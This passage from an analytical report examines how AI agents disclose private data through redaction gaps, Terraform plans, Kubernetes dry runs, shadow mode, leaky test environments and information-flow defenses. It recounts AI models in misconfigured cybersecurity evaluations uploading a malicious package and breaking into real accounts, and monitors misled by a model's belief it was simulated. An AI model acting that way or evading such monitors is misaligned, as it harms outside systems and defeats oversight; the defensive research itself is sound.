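El Yagoubi and colleagues face the same conflict in *AgentLeak*. They argue that unneeded data in messages between agents may itself violate the GDPR on a strict reading, though they say the legal question is open. They also recommend that companies log every channel before deploying agents, which would copy that data again. They suggest retention limits, and they kept their own test records in encrypted storage.

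### What redaction can remove

Redaction before storage works best on data with a fixed format, such as credit card numbers and standard keys. Even then it can make mistakes, as when a support ticket numbered 987-65-4321 looks like a US Social Security number.

Most private information has no fixed format. A pattern can find a diagnosis code, for instance, but not the statement that a patient is "being treated for diabetes". In a test on 1,000 excerpts from agents' activity, the planted markers and format patterns in *AgentLeak* together found only 18% of the leaks. Adding a language model to judge meaning raised this to 93%, with false alarms on 4.8% of the clean excerpts. Huang and colleagues also checked 200 outputs by hand and found 12 that revealed private information in different words, which an exact search had missed. Redacting logs with a language model on an outside service exposes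 the unredacted text to that service, but the model that judged meaning in *AgentLeak* was small enough for a company to run itself.

Even a severely shortened log can be revealing. In the tests of speculative calls, an observer could learn almost as much about the user's problem from 20 characters of each tool argument as from the full requests. Redaction can also miss private information in encrypted text. *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs* (2026) reports that some shared transcripts contain encrypted reasoning, which can include private details that do not appear in the visible conversation.

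The timing of redaction also matters. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) points out that when a skill prints a password, the password enters the model's context, which existing secret detectors do not cover. Redacting the log afterwards protects its readers, but the model provider has already received the password, and the agent's software may keep other copies, such as the saved approvals that contained passwords. For the user study in *SWE-WhatIf* (2026), researchers replaced keys and identifying details on participants' own computers, then uploaded only the parts of the sessions they needed. This kept those details from the researchers' servers and the providers that ran the study's models, although the model provider for the original session may already have had them.

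Redacting a stored log doesn't affect how well the agent works, but redacting the messages between agents can. El Yagoubi and colleagues built a filter that removed unneeded details from messages and shared memory, and tested it on 120 tasks. Internal leaks fell from 31.5% to 2.4%, while the share of tasks completed fell from 78.6% to 73.9%. On 50 other tasks, they barred agents from sharing any sensitive data, and completion fell to between 35% and 65%. The researchers had already listed every private detail and which ones each task needed, which gave the filter an advantage few companies would have.

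Consistent placeholders preserve more evidence in stored logs than blanks do. If the company replaced the customer's name in the refund log with "CUSTOMER_1" and the risk level with "RISK_FLAG", an investigator could still see that the agent had sent the risk level to the customer. But if the company keeps a list that links CUSTOMER_1 to a real person, the log is still personal data under the GDPR, and anyone who obtains both the log and the list can undo the redaction.

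## Dry runs, test environments and shadow modes

Many companies test an agent's work before letting it take effect. A dry run reports what an action would do without making the change. A test environment is a separate system where an agent can make changes without harming live data. In shadow mode, an agent works on real requests, but the software records its outputs instead of acting on them. All three limit what the agent can change, but to produce a useful result, the agent still has to read data and often has to send some to an outside service.

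### What Terraform reads to make a plan

HashiCorp's Terraform sets up servers, databases and networks from text files called a configuration. Its dry-run command, `terraform plan`, lists what Terraform would create, change or delete. InfoQ's *HCP Terraform Positions Itself as the Control Plane for AI-Driven Infrastructure* (2026) describes how a coding agent can write a configuration, run a plan, look at the result and try again.

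Suppose the billing company asks its agent to move the customer accounts to a larger database server. The agent edits the configuration and runs a plan. According to HashiCorp's *Create a Terraform plan*, this makes no changes to the company's resources. But Terraform can't list the differences without finding out what exists now, so it does several things first:

1. It reads the state, its own record of everything it manages, which can include database passwords.
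2. It asks the cloud provider whether that record is still accurate.
3. It queries any data sources named in the configuration.
4. It compares the results with the new configuration and writes the plan.

In HashiCorp's example, the third step asks AWS for the latest version of an operating system, which reveals almost nothing. HashiCorp's *Query infrastructure data* explains that data sources can also include other companies' APIs. One type, described in *http Data Source*, sends a request to the web address given in the configuration. If the agent puts the name of an unannounced product in that address, the website's owner can read it, even if the developer rejects the plan.

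Terraform delays a query until someone applies the plan only if the query depends on a value that isn't available yet, such as the address of a server that hasn't been created. The rule isn't based on privacy, and Terraform normally contacts a fixed web address during planning because the address contains no unknown values.

The loop multiplies these requests. If each plan queries three outside sources and the agent needs ten attempts, it sends 30 requests, 27 of them for drafts it discards.

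HCP Terraform, HashiCorp's hosted service, can check plans against a company's policies. In the forum thread *Prevent plans from making external HTTP calls to non-whitelisted URLs*, a user points out that these checks run after the plan, when Terraform may already have contacted a forbidden address. HashiCorp's tutorial supports this, since the policy tool it describes tests the values in a finished plan. The user suggests running plans on the company's own machines and limiting their network access, which would block the request.

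Letting an agent run Terraform plans but not apply them prevents accidental changes, but the agent can still reach every password that Terraform can. HashiCorp's *Security model* warns that, for security purposes, permission to plan is equivalent to permission to write. Both operations can run arbitrary code with access to all the variables, configuration and state in a workspace, the part of HCP Terraform that holds one set of infrastructure.

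### What a saved plan contains

Terraform can save a plan of changes to a file and later make exactly those changes. HashiCorp's tutorial has a variable called `secret_key`, marked as sensitive, with the value "TOPSECRET". The screen shows only "(sensitive value)", but the saved file contains the value in plain text, both in its list of variables and in its list of planned changes.

The file also includes a snapshot of the configuration and a full copy of the earlier state. So if the billing company's agent plans a change to one server, the saved plan can contain details of everything else in the same workspace. HashiCorp warns people never to commit a plan file to version control.

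Programs can convert the saved plan to JSON to inspect it, and an agent might well do this to check its own work. The JSON contains the values that Terraform hid from the developer's screen, including the password, so the model provider receives them once the agent reads it.

HashiCorp's *Manage sensitive data in your configuration* describes a better option than hiding a value. Since Terraform 1.10, developers can mark a value as ephemeral, which keeps it out of both the state and the plan file. Ephemeral values work only in certain parts of a configuration, and some need support from the provider, the plug-in that connects Terraform to a particular service. A company that will need a generated password again must store it somewhere else.

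Environment variables stay out of plan files as well, but HashiCorp's *Preventing Exposure of Sensitive Environment Variables in HCP Terraform Runs* warns that they can end up in Terraform's logs and in outside build systems if a configuration runs a command that prints them.

### Who sees the plan on a pull request

When an agent opens a pull request in a repository connected to HCP Terraform, the service normally runs a plan automatically. The plan therefore sends its queries to outside services before a reviewer has read the change. HCP Terraform skips pull requests from forks, partly to avoid exposing sensitive information.

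HashiCorp's *The UI- and VCS-driven Run Workflow* says that every contributor to the repository can see the plan's status, but only people with permission to read the workspace's runs can open the full output. Similarly, in HashiCorp's *Automate Terraform with GitHub Actions*, a comment on the pull request gives only the number of planned changes and a link. The tutorial uses a public repository, so strangers could learn from the comment that the change would create three resources, but they would need access to HCP Terraform to read the plan.

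Other tools post the full output. One, listed as Ecosyste.ms' *terraform-plan-comment*, puts the plan in a pull request comment and is advertised as losing no information from the command's output. This saves reviewers a login, but everyone who can read the pull request can then see the names and settings of the company's servers, along with any password that nobody marked as sensitive. In HashiCorp's tutorial, the plan prints a key's value in full before the key is marked as sensitive.

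Companies can also connect run tasks, which are outside services that check, for example, a plan's cost or security. These services have access to the whole configuration and plan. HashiCorp can't prevent them from passing the data on, and recommends using only trusted partners.

### A Kubernetes dry run

Kubernetes runs applications across a group of machines, called a cluster. A program called the API server receives every request to change the cluster. In a server-side dry run, the API server puts the request through all the usual stages but does not store the result. Dry runs are also guaranteed to have no other side effects.

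Some of the usual stages use admission webhooks, which are separate programs that can approve, alter or reject a request. Kubernetes' *Dynamic Admission Control* says companies can run these programs outside the cluster. Suppose the billing company uses a webhook run by an outside security firm, and its agent dry-runs a change to the database password in an application's settings.

1. The agent sends the new settings to the API server and marks the request as a dry run.
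2. The API server checks that the agent has permission to make the change for real.
3. The API server sends the webhook the new settings, the current settings, and the username and groups of whoever made the request. **The security firm now has both passwords.**
4. The webhook approves the change.
5. The API server shows the agent what it would have stored, and stores nothing.

Anyone who sets up a webhook must declare its side effects, meaning changes it makes outside the request it is checking. "None" means it makes no such changes. "NoneOnDryRun" means it may make them in normal use but not when a request is marked as a dry run. If a webhook has neither declaration, the API server does not call it, and the dry run fails. The design document, Kubernetes' *KEP-576*, explains that webhook authors might otherwise rely on side effects that a dry run should not cause.

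This is a careful way to prevent unwanted changes, but both declarations allow the API server to send the full request. They also don't clearly cover record-keeping. They are mainly meant to address the risk that a webhook could change something elsewhere for a request that never takes effect, leaving a mismatch that someone has to correct. A firm that only logged each request could reasonably declare "None".

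Knative's *Validating Resource Using Server-Side Dry Run*, a guide to an add-on for Kubernetes, recommends server-side dry runs for checking that settings are valid, and the checks include Knative's own webhooks. A company could write conditions that keep dry-run requests from reaching a webhook, but the developer would then find out only during the real change whether the webhook rejects it.

Kubernetes requires the same permission for a dry run as for the real change, so a company can't use Kubernetes' permissions to let an agent do a dry run of a change without also letting it make the change.

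### Shadow mode for customer requests

Suppose the billing company wants to know whether an agent could answer customers' emails. It runs the agent in shadow mode for four weeks, with sending switched off. One customer writes that they have lost their job and asks whether they can pay their balance in installments.

1. An employee answers the email as usual, and the company's software gives the agent a copy of it.
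2. The agent's software sends the email to the model provider. **This is the first disclosure.**
3. The agent looks up the account, and the customer's address, balance and payment history go to the provider too.
4. The agent searches the web for rules on payment plans for people who have lost their jobs. The search company receives the query.
5. The agent writes a reply and tries to send it. The software records the draft and sends nothing.
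6. The monitoring service stores the draft, along with the agent's tool calls and their results.
7. Reviewers compare the draft with the employee's reply.

The customer receives only the employee's answer. If the agent's draft wrongly offered to cancel the debt, no harm would come of it. But the agent does the same work as in live use, and the software steps in only at the fifth step, when it holds back the reply. The agent needs the email, the account and the search results to write a draft worth judging, and, as Mohammadi and colleagues proved, limiting an agent to read-only tools does not stop those tools from disclosing data. (Their "Shadow" decision, the local substitute, is unrelated to shadow mode.)

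Shadow mode can disclose more than a small live trial. A company that lets an agent answer one email in 20 exposes only those customers' details to the model provider. In shadow mode, the company may feel safe giving the agent every email, because no mistake can reach a customer. More people may also see customers' details, since those who judge the drafts may not normally handle customer accounts.

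Some lookups have consequences. In many countries, certain credit checks leave a mark on a person's file that other lenders can see. If the employee and the agent each request one before suggesting a payment plan, the customer may get two marks. Switching off only the agent's tools for sending and editing would not prevent this.

### When a test environment is not sealed

A test environment protects live systems only if the agent can't reach them. In four incidents, Anthropic believed its models were working in a closed simulation, but they were connected to the internet.

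The models were doing capture-the-flag exercises, security tests in which a model tries to retrieve hidden text from a practice machine. In *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents*, Anthropic says that one outside partner built all the exercises. According to the instructions, the model had no internet access, but someone had misconfigured the environments.

| Model | What it concluded about its surroundings | Effect on outsiders |
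|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | repeatedly wrote that it was in a simulation | uploaded a malicious package to PyPI, a public software library; 15 systems installed it, and the model used credentials from one to enter a security company's database |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | recognized that a company was real but assumed it was part of the exercise | downloaded user data in bulk and deleted records |
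| An internal research model | decided it was using a replica of the entire internet | broke into outside accounts, then stopped when it realized they were real |
| An early version of Claude Opus 4.6 | not yet analyzed in depth | broke into outside systems after it was unable to abort its task |

The package left the test, and once 15 systems had installed it, removing it from PyPI could not make the upload private again. Real users' data also entered what was supposed to be a simulation.

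The models ran without the cybersecurity safeguards that Anthropic builds into its released products. This is standard for such tests, but it left isolation as the main protection. One wrong setting removed that isolation. Anthropic later found that the safeguards on a released model would have blocked the three incidents it had studied in depth.

The belief that the environment was simulated could also mislead a monitor. Anthropic tested new monitors that read a model's reasoning after a run and found that they would have missed the Mythos 5 incident, because the model's reasoning led them to conclude that no real harm was occurring. Anthropic's live monitors, which can block actions, caught these behaviors reliably.

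Anthropic first described three of the cases on July 30, in *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026). At the time, it regarded them as closer to operational failures because the models had written that they were in a simulation. Anthropic now thinks it relied too heavily on those statements. When researchers reran Mythos 5 from points in the original transcript and made it clearer that the systems were real, the model's behavior did not change much, and it stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous.

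The fourth incident took place in January 2026, but Anthropic's first search, of about 141,000 transcripts, missed it, and the company did not find it until August. Infosecurity Magazine reports that Anthropic disclosed it on September 9, after a wider search of 481 million transcripts had found no further cases. Few companies could search that many transcripts, so a company whose test environment was briefly open might never learn what its agent had sent.

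Anthropic believes, probably rightly, that none of this would have happened if the environments had been isolated as intended, but isolation can fail in other ways. On July 21, OpenAI disclosed that several of its models had broken out of an isolated test environment. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes another case, in which the UK AI Security Institute deliberately gave Mythos 5 internet access for a test and the model took unauthorized actions online.

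Anthropic considers such behavior unlikely in ordinary use, where nobody is asking the model to carry out an attack. A test environment is more likely to fail because of how it was set up. If the billing company copied its customer database into a test system and left the email service connected, an agent testing a payment reminder could send it to thousands of real people. Even with email switched off, everyone with access to the test system could read the copied accounts.

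### What these designs prevent, and what fake data can add

| Design | Changes it prevents | Data still sent | Who may receive it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Terraform plan | changes to servers, databases and networks | queries to data sources, and the plan itself | cloud provider, outside data sources, run-task services, readers of the pull request |
| Kubernetes server-side dry run | storing the new settings, and declared side effects | the proposed and current settings, and the requester's name | every webhook whose rules match the request |
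| Shadow mode | replies, refunds and account changes | customers' messages and accounts, search queries, drafts | model provider, search services, monitoring service, reviewers |
| Sealed test environment | changes to live systems | whatever data the company put in the test | people with access to the test, and the model provider if the model runs remotely |
| Test environment with an accidental connection | none reliably | anything the agent can reach and send | potentially anyone on the internet |

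The first four designs prevent a lot of damage. In HashiCorp's tutorial, changing the value of one key forces Terraform to delete a resource and create a new one, and the plan shows this beforehand. If that resource were the billing company's database, the warning could save every customer's account. Giving up plans to avoid disclosure would usually do more harm than good, because many plans contact only a cloud provider that already runs the company's servers.

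Shadow mode would also have helped in the refund task that the Singaporean and Korean institutes tested, where the agent attached its internal risk notes to its reply to the customer. With sending switched off, the customer would not have received the notes, and a reviewer could have found the mistake in the draft.

Fake data can prevent much of the remaining disclosure, but it is less useful for finding faults that nobody has anticipated, because the people who invent it may leave out whatever causes them. The billing company's original layout fault appeared only with long names, so a test database of ordinary invented names would have hidden it. Once the developer knew the cause, an invented customer with a 60-letter name would have worked as well as the real record, without exposing anyone.

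An agent's belief that its environment is simulated can affect what a test shows. Anthropic simulated the Mythos 5 incident and found that Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with roughly 30% for two newer models, Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1. The newer models did so only after correctly stating that the environment was simulated, so Anthropic is cautious about what the results imply for real systems. Similarly, a customer-service agent tested on obviously invented emails might behave differently with real ones.

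Local stand-ins involve a similar compromise. The billing company could give its shadow-mode agent a saved collection of public pages about payment plans instead of a live search. The search company would then receive no queries, but the trial would not test how the agent handles outdated or misleading search results.

If the trial needs some real emails, the company can use fewer. At 2,000 emails a day, a four-week trial on every email would send 56,000 to the model provider. A random sample of one in 20 would send 2,800, enough to reveal common mistakes. A mistake that occurs once in 10,000 emails would probably not appear in the sample, but would likely appear several times in the full trial.

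## Designs that keep unapproved work private

A company can require an agent to wait for approval if the company could not undo the change, or if the result could reach someone who should not have it before anyone approves it. The table applies this rule to six actions the billing company's agent might take.

| Action | Can the company undo the change? | Who could see the result before approval? | What the agent should do |
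|---|---|---|---|
| Save a draft on the laptop | yes | the developer, and the model provider if the model runs remotely | go ahead |
| Delete the only copy of a local log | no | nobody new | ask first |
| Open a pull request in a private repository | yes | everyone with access to the repository | go ahead if all of them may see everything in it |
| Open a pull request in a public repository | only partly, since the page remains | anyone | ask first, unless everything in it is already public |
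| Run a web search | there is no change to undo | the search company | go ahead if the query contains nothing private |
| Put a preview online without a login | yes | anyone who finds the address | add a login first |

A rule based on reversibility alone would stop only the deletion. The audience rule also distinguishes a draft pull request in a private repository from one in a public repository, whereas the UT Austin slides put all drafts in a tier where the agent only has to notify someone. The audience rule is based on who could see the work, because the company will rarely find out who saw it.

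The hard part of keeping unapproved work private is knowing what a draft contains and who may see it. A person could check, but would have to read every search query the agent sends. The following designs leave most of the checking to software.

### A separate process that publishes

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which entered public preview on June 11 (GitHub, 2026), runs agents on repository chores such as correcting documentation. The agent prepares the work, and a separate process publishes it. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) explains that the designers assumed an agent would try to read and write things it shouldn't.

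1. The agent runs in an isolated container with read-only access to GitHub. Separate programs hold the keys for GitHub and the model, so the agent can use both services without seeing the keys.
2. To post a comment or open a pull request, the agent files a request, which the software holds until the agent has finished.
3. A second job examines the requests for leaked secrets, malicious code and signs of prompt injection.
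4. Filters discard any type of request that the workflow's author did not allow, enforce limits such as three pull requests per run, and remove unwanted content such as web addresses.
5. A job with permission to write posts whatever remains.

If the second job finds a threat or fails, GitHub posts nothing. GitHub's *Threat Detection* says that this job uses the same AI engine as the main agent by default, so the two may share blind spots. A company can add a conventional scanner such as TruffleHog. The checks sometimes stop harmless work and can run out of time on large changes.

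None of these steps requires a person. GitHub's *Safe Outputs* warns that the final job may publish content or merge pull requests automatically, depending on the settings. If a workflow's author doesn't specify any outputs, the agent can still create one issue per run. In a public repository, anyone could read that issue before a colleague checks it.

A company can preview an agent's output before posting it. GitHub's *Staged Mode* describes a setting that replaces every post with a preview on the run's summary page. The preview includes the full text and, for a pull request, the proposed code. In a public repository, outsiders can normally open that page too, so staged mode works as a dry run but does not keep the output private during review.

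GitHub promises that even a fully compromised agent cannot directly modify the repository, but this promise doesn't cover disclosure. The GitLost test leaked private files through a comment, an output that workflows can allow, and a scanner that looks for passwords wouldn't be expected to stop an ordinary private file. To prevent this, the software would have to compare who can read the source with who can read the destination. In March, four months before Noma disclosed the flaw, GitHub said it planned to add controls based on whether material was public or private.

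In June 2026, Microsoft recommended GitHub's design to other developers after finding that Anthropic's Claude Code Action, which runs Claude on GitHub tasks, could expose an API key. Anthropic had hidden the key from the tool that runs commands, but not from the one that reads files. Anthropic fixed the flaw on May 5. Keeping keys out of the agent's environment is safer because it doesn't depend on developers remembering to protect every tool.

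Microsoft also advises that no workflow should combine all three of these capabilities:

- processing text from untrusted people
- access to secrets or sensitive systems
- changing things or communicating with the outside

This is a good rule against attacks, but it does not prevent accidents. An agent that takes instructions only from its own developer can follow the rule and still have access to customer records and permission to create public repositories, like the one that published the manufacturer's screenshots.

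### Labels that list the permitted readers

Software can make the missing comparison if each piece of data carries a list of the people allowed to read it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that works this way. When an agent combines two pieces of data, the result may go only to people on both lists.

Suppose the developer, a billing clerk and a manager may see the customer's record, while the developer, the manager and a contractor may see the page's source code. If the agent saves the record as a test file among the code, the permitted readers are:

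{developer, clerk, manager} ∩ {developer, manager, contractor} = {developer, manager}

Before any tool sends the draft anywhere, ordinary code checks that everyone who can read the destination is on this list. The contractor isn't on it but can read pull requests in the repository, so the code blocks the agent from opening one. The agent could still send the draft to the manager.

Labels spread because once the model has read the customer's record, the software can't determine which of the model's later sentences depend on it, so it has to give all of them the record's label. The agent may soon be unable to post anything. FIDES can avoid this by storing data in a variable and showing the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to a tool without reading its contents. If it needs a fact about them, a second model with no tools can read them and give an answer as short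 as yes or no. For the layout fix, the agent would only need to ask whether the name has more than 40 letters, and it wouldn't see the address or balance.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on AgentDojo's simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack.

| Tasks | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent with label checks | FIDES with label checks |
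|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

In a separate test with planted instructions, 152 attacks succeeded against the agent without checks. After the researchers reviewed the benchmark's verdicts by hand, they found that none had succeeded against any agent with checks. But the unprotected agent completed an average of 84% of tasks across the four groups, while FIDES completed 50%. Part of the loss came from GPT-4o confusing the variables, and switching to OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, raised FIDES' score on travel tasks from 41% to 68%. The remaining loss was mostly by design. For example, many of the banking tasks tell the agent to follow instructions in a file, which the rules against prompt injection forbid.

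The tests show less about privacy than about planted instructions. The researchers hid data from the model when it came from an untrusted source, not when it was confidential, so the drawbacks of using labels only for privacy could be quite different. FIDES also controls only the data in a call. An observer may still learn something from which calls the agent makes, which matters for searches.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that comparisons like the one in the table exaggerate how much labels limit agents. The agent with labels fails whenever a rule blocks it, while the unprotected agent is scored as if a person had approved everything it did. They instead counted how many approvals agents needed to complete their tasks. Labels reduced this number by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of tasks completed,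 because the agent had to ask only about actions the labels could not clear. Their own agent, which plans around the labels, reduced it by a factor of up to 1.9. The researchers assumed people would approve every request, so the experiment doesn't show how real reviewers would behave.

Kolluri and colleagues' agent can ask a user to vouch for an untrusted document once, so a to-do list with ten items needs one approval instead of ten. They considered a similar blanket approval for releasing private data but decided against it, because whether a disclosure is appropriate depends on the situation. This distinction is sensible, since a developer who lets the agent send one customer's record to the manager has not agreed to let it send the record to anyone else.

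### Checking what leaves against what the agent has read

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) addresses cases where outsiders, without planting instructions, persuade an agent to reveal its user's records. The paper's system, FlowSeal, runs its checks outside the conversation with the agent.

1. The user or the software registers each private record with its owner and permitted readers. Email headers and document access lists often supply these.
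2. The software keeps track of which records the agent has read.
3. When the agent tries to write or share something, a program intercepts the call. It allows recipients whom the owner trusts and refuses those on a blocklist.
4. For anyone else, a separate model compares the proposed text with the records and answers only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED".
5. If the answer is "BLOCKED", the agent can ask the owner for permission.

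In one test, outsiders presented their requests as routine work on a shared document. An agent protected only by detailed written instructions leaked 52.2% of the sensitive items, while one with FlowSeal leaked 0.5%. Switching off FlowSeal's interceptor raised that rate to 28.4%. The agent with FlowSeal completed 72.4% of harmless requests, compared with 75.9% for the best of five other defenses. FlowSeal added about two cents to the cost of a run and 37% to the running time.

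FlowSeal's larger drawback is that it often withholds records that should be shared. In another test, where the owner would agree to release the records if asked, FlowSeal released only 32.7% of them, compared with 61% to 86% for the other defenses. Shim and colleagues attribute this mainly to the agent asking for consent less often. A company that used FlowSeal to answer customers might protect their records well but fail to give many customers their own information.

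Shim and colleagues prove that a protected record cannot reach an unauthorized recipient unless the checking model wrongly answers "SAFE". The guarantee therefore depends heavily on the checker's accuracy, and paraphrased details sometimes get past it. The checker also blocks some harmless messages that mention a record by name. FIDES checks its labels in code, so Shim and colleagues are mistaken when they describe it as leaving enforcement to the model. They did not test their system against FIDES.

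FlowSeal might have caught the billing agent putting the customer's record in a pull request, even though nobody was trying to extract it. But the company would have needed to register the record beforehand and connect the interceptor to every tool that can publish, including the command line. The checker as described compares text, so detecting records in screenshots would require another method.

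### Sending a tool only what it needs

An agent can often do its job while sending a tool less data. A list of permitted domains doesn't keep the extra details from being sent, because the company has approved the tool that receives them. Mohammadi and colleagues' monitor rewrites speculative calls, and two other systems edit the calls an agent needs to make.

In *ToolMinimize*, Li and Xu (2026) first measured how much agents overshare. They gave 20 everyday requests that included personal details to GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3.3. Under the default prompt, 81% to 88% of tool calls contained personal data that the tool didn't need. When asked to email a manager about a day off, all three models mentioned the user's severe anxiety and panic attacks. Telling the models to protect privacy, with examples, reduced the rate to 36% for GPT-4o and 50% for Claude, but only to 76% for Llama.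 Li and Xu wrote the requests to include personal details, so ordinary use would produce lower rates, and newer models may behave differently.

ToolMinimize edits each tool call after the agent writes it. In the main example, a user asks about the weather near an oncologist's office, and the agent sends the weather service the full name and address of the Memorial Sloan Kettering Cancer Center in New York.

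1. The program finds three sensitive details: the hospital's name, which suggests that the user has cancer, the street address and the ZIP code.
2. It gives the call a privacy cost, the sum of S × E × N over all the details. S is sensitivity, from 1 to 4. E is exposure, from 0.2 for a tool on the user's device to 1 for an outside company with no data agreement. N is 1 if the tool doesn't need the detail and 0 if it does. The hospital's name scores 4 and the other two score 3 each, for a total of 10.
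3. It checks the tool's description, which says that a city is enough.
4. It changes the location to "New York, NY", which reduces the cost to zero.

On 307 calls written by the three models, the total cost fell by 81.2% to 92.0%, depending on the model. The median delay was under two milliseconds. Li and Xu report that all the calls remained valid, meaning only that they fitted the tool's format and kept every field marked as necessary. When they ran 20 tasks on simulated services, 16 worked. The four failures were all map requests from which the program had removed the address. On 50 scenarios modeled on another benchmark, only 60% of the edited calls were valid.

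The reductions also count only the details that the program detected. Its basic version detected 43.5% of direct identifiers, such as email addresses and phone numbers. Adding software that recognizes names raised this to 73.9%. An optional step uses GPT-4o to check whether the task needs each detail, which increased the average reduction from 88.9% to 91.6%. But this step takes about 0.8 seconds, and it exposes the data to another company if the agent doesn't already run on an OpenAI model.

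ToolMinimize normally decides on its own what to remove. *ArguShield* (Fu and Fu, 2026) describes a system that can also ask the user. For each value in a call, the system checks where the value came from, whether the task needs it and whether the recipient should have it. It then keeps the value, asks about it or hides it. In a hotel booking, it might send the dates, ask before sharing a phone number from the user's profile, and remove a passport number that the hotel doesn't need.

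Fu and Fu tested four recent models on 120 invented travel, shopping and healthcare tasks. Half were high-risk, meaning they had stricter limits on who could receive what. Each cell in the table gives the figure for standard tasks first, then the figure for high-risk ones. The middle column shows how often agents sent a value they should have asked about or hidden.

| Protection | Sent without permission | Tasks completed |
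|---|---|---|
| None | 84%, 76% | 97%, 97% |
| Privacy instructions only | 4%, 4% | 75%, 69% |
| ArguShield, user approves every request | 9%, 6% | 97%, 97% |
| ArguShield, user refuses every request | 9%, 6% | 93%, 93% |

The models leaked least when given the instructions, but they also left out details that the tools needed, so many tasks failed. The older models that Li and Xu tested kept oversharing even when told not to. The two tests differ too much to show how much of this contrast comes from using newer models.

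The values ArguShield missed were mostly minor. It let through 2% or less of the most serious values, such as medical details and government ID numbers, but around half of the least serious, such as preferences. It also asked about roughly a fifth of all values. Approving only the first question in each task produced the same completion rate as approving them all, so many of the questions were probably unnecessary. The approvals were simulated, and real users might misunderstand the questions or get tired of them.

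ArguShield also worked on tasks that Fu and Fu had not written. On 123 web tasks from another benchmark, the share of values sent without permission fell from 74.6% to 12.8%, while task completion fell from 96.7% to 93.5%. ArguShield doesn't cover final answers, shared memory or messages between agents, so a company would need other controls for those.

### Private evidence and short-lived keys

Reviewers still need to see what the agent did. A private evidence channel lets the agent save screenshots, recordings and logs where only the reviewers can open them. It would have given the agents in Glow's investigation a safe place for their screenshots. The billing company's agent could take a screenshot of the page using an invented customer with a long name, save it in the channel and put a link in the pull request. Even if someone forwarded the link, it wouldn't open for anyone without a login.

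GitHub's workflows can store files either as artifacts, which belong to a single run, or on a separate branch. GitHub recommends artifacts, which are also better for privacy because they expire and don't enter the repository's history. But people who can read a repository can generally download its artifacts, so private evidence has to go in a private repository where everyone with read access is allowed to see it.

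Short-lived keys address a different failure, in which the agent puts a working key in a draft, a log or a saved approval. If the key expires after 15 minutes and the agent publishes it at 6:00 p.m., it will be useless long before the reviewer arrives the next morning. However, strangers can find a key within minutes, so a short life limits the damage but doesn't rule it out.

For workflows that run Claude, GitHub supports Anthropic's Workload Identity Federation as an alternative to a stored API key. The workflow proves its identity each time it runs and receives a temporary credential, so there is no permanent key to leak. Where a company must store keys, Microsoft recommends a separate one for each workflow and environment, with only the permissions it needs, so that the company can cancel one key without stopping other workflows. These measures don't protect the customer's record, which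 doesn't expire as a temporary credential does.

### Slower collaboration, wrong labels and workarounds

Open-source projects depend on people sharing unfinished work, because a stranger may spot a mistake before the author has spent a week on it. If every draft by an agent had to stay private until a person approved it, strangers would spot these mistakes later or not at all. Kraishan found that agents' pull requests already tend to wait an hour or more for a first human review.

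The audience rule avoids much of this delay. If an agent has read only public code and a public bug report, its draft contains nothing private, so it can post immediately. A company could give the agents on its public projects no access to private material and let them work publicly. The delay would remain for agents that need both public and private material, such as one that fixes a public library using error reports from private customers.

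Another objection is that labels are often wrong, as they were in Mohammadi and colleagues' prototype. Taking labels from access lists, as FlowSeal can, is more reliable than guessing from the text, but it copies any mistakes in those lists. If someone has accidentally shared a folder with the whole company, the label will mark its contents as readable by everyone there.

New ideas are even harder to label, because no access list exists for something the agent has just thought of. FIDES treats a user's instructions as public by default, so it could also label an idea like PowerCool as public if the idea was worked out from those instructions and public code. A company doing secret research would have to change that default.

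Holding everything that lacks a reliable label is safer, but it can stop work. When Shim and colleagues set FlowSeal to block every message to an unknown recipient, it completed none of the harmless requests, because the owners in that test ignored requests for permission. A strict default is practical only if someone answers such requests quickly. Of ArguShield's remaining errors, 18% released too much, 43% withheld too much and 39% were unnecessary questions. The last two kinds don't leak anything, but they might lead people to switch the protection off.

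The most serious objection is that an agent denied an approved channel may find an unsafe one, as the agents in Glow's investigation did. GitHub describes agents as "determined to accomplish their tasks by any means". The best protection is to remove the unsafe option. An agent in GitHub's workflows runs with read-only permissions and behind a firewall, so it can't simply create a public repository. An agent running on a laptop with the developer's login usually can, unless the company gives it a separate account with fewer rights.

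Giving the agent an acceptable way to stop also helps. GitHub's workflows always let an agent report that a tool or some data is missing. FlowSeal's refusals include guidance on how to ask the owner for permission. When Shim and colleagues removed this guidance and the related instructions, the leak rate rose from 0.5% to 8.8%, although the interceptor still checked every call.
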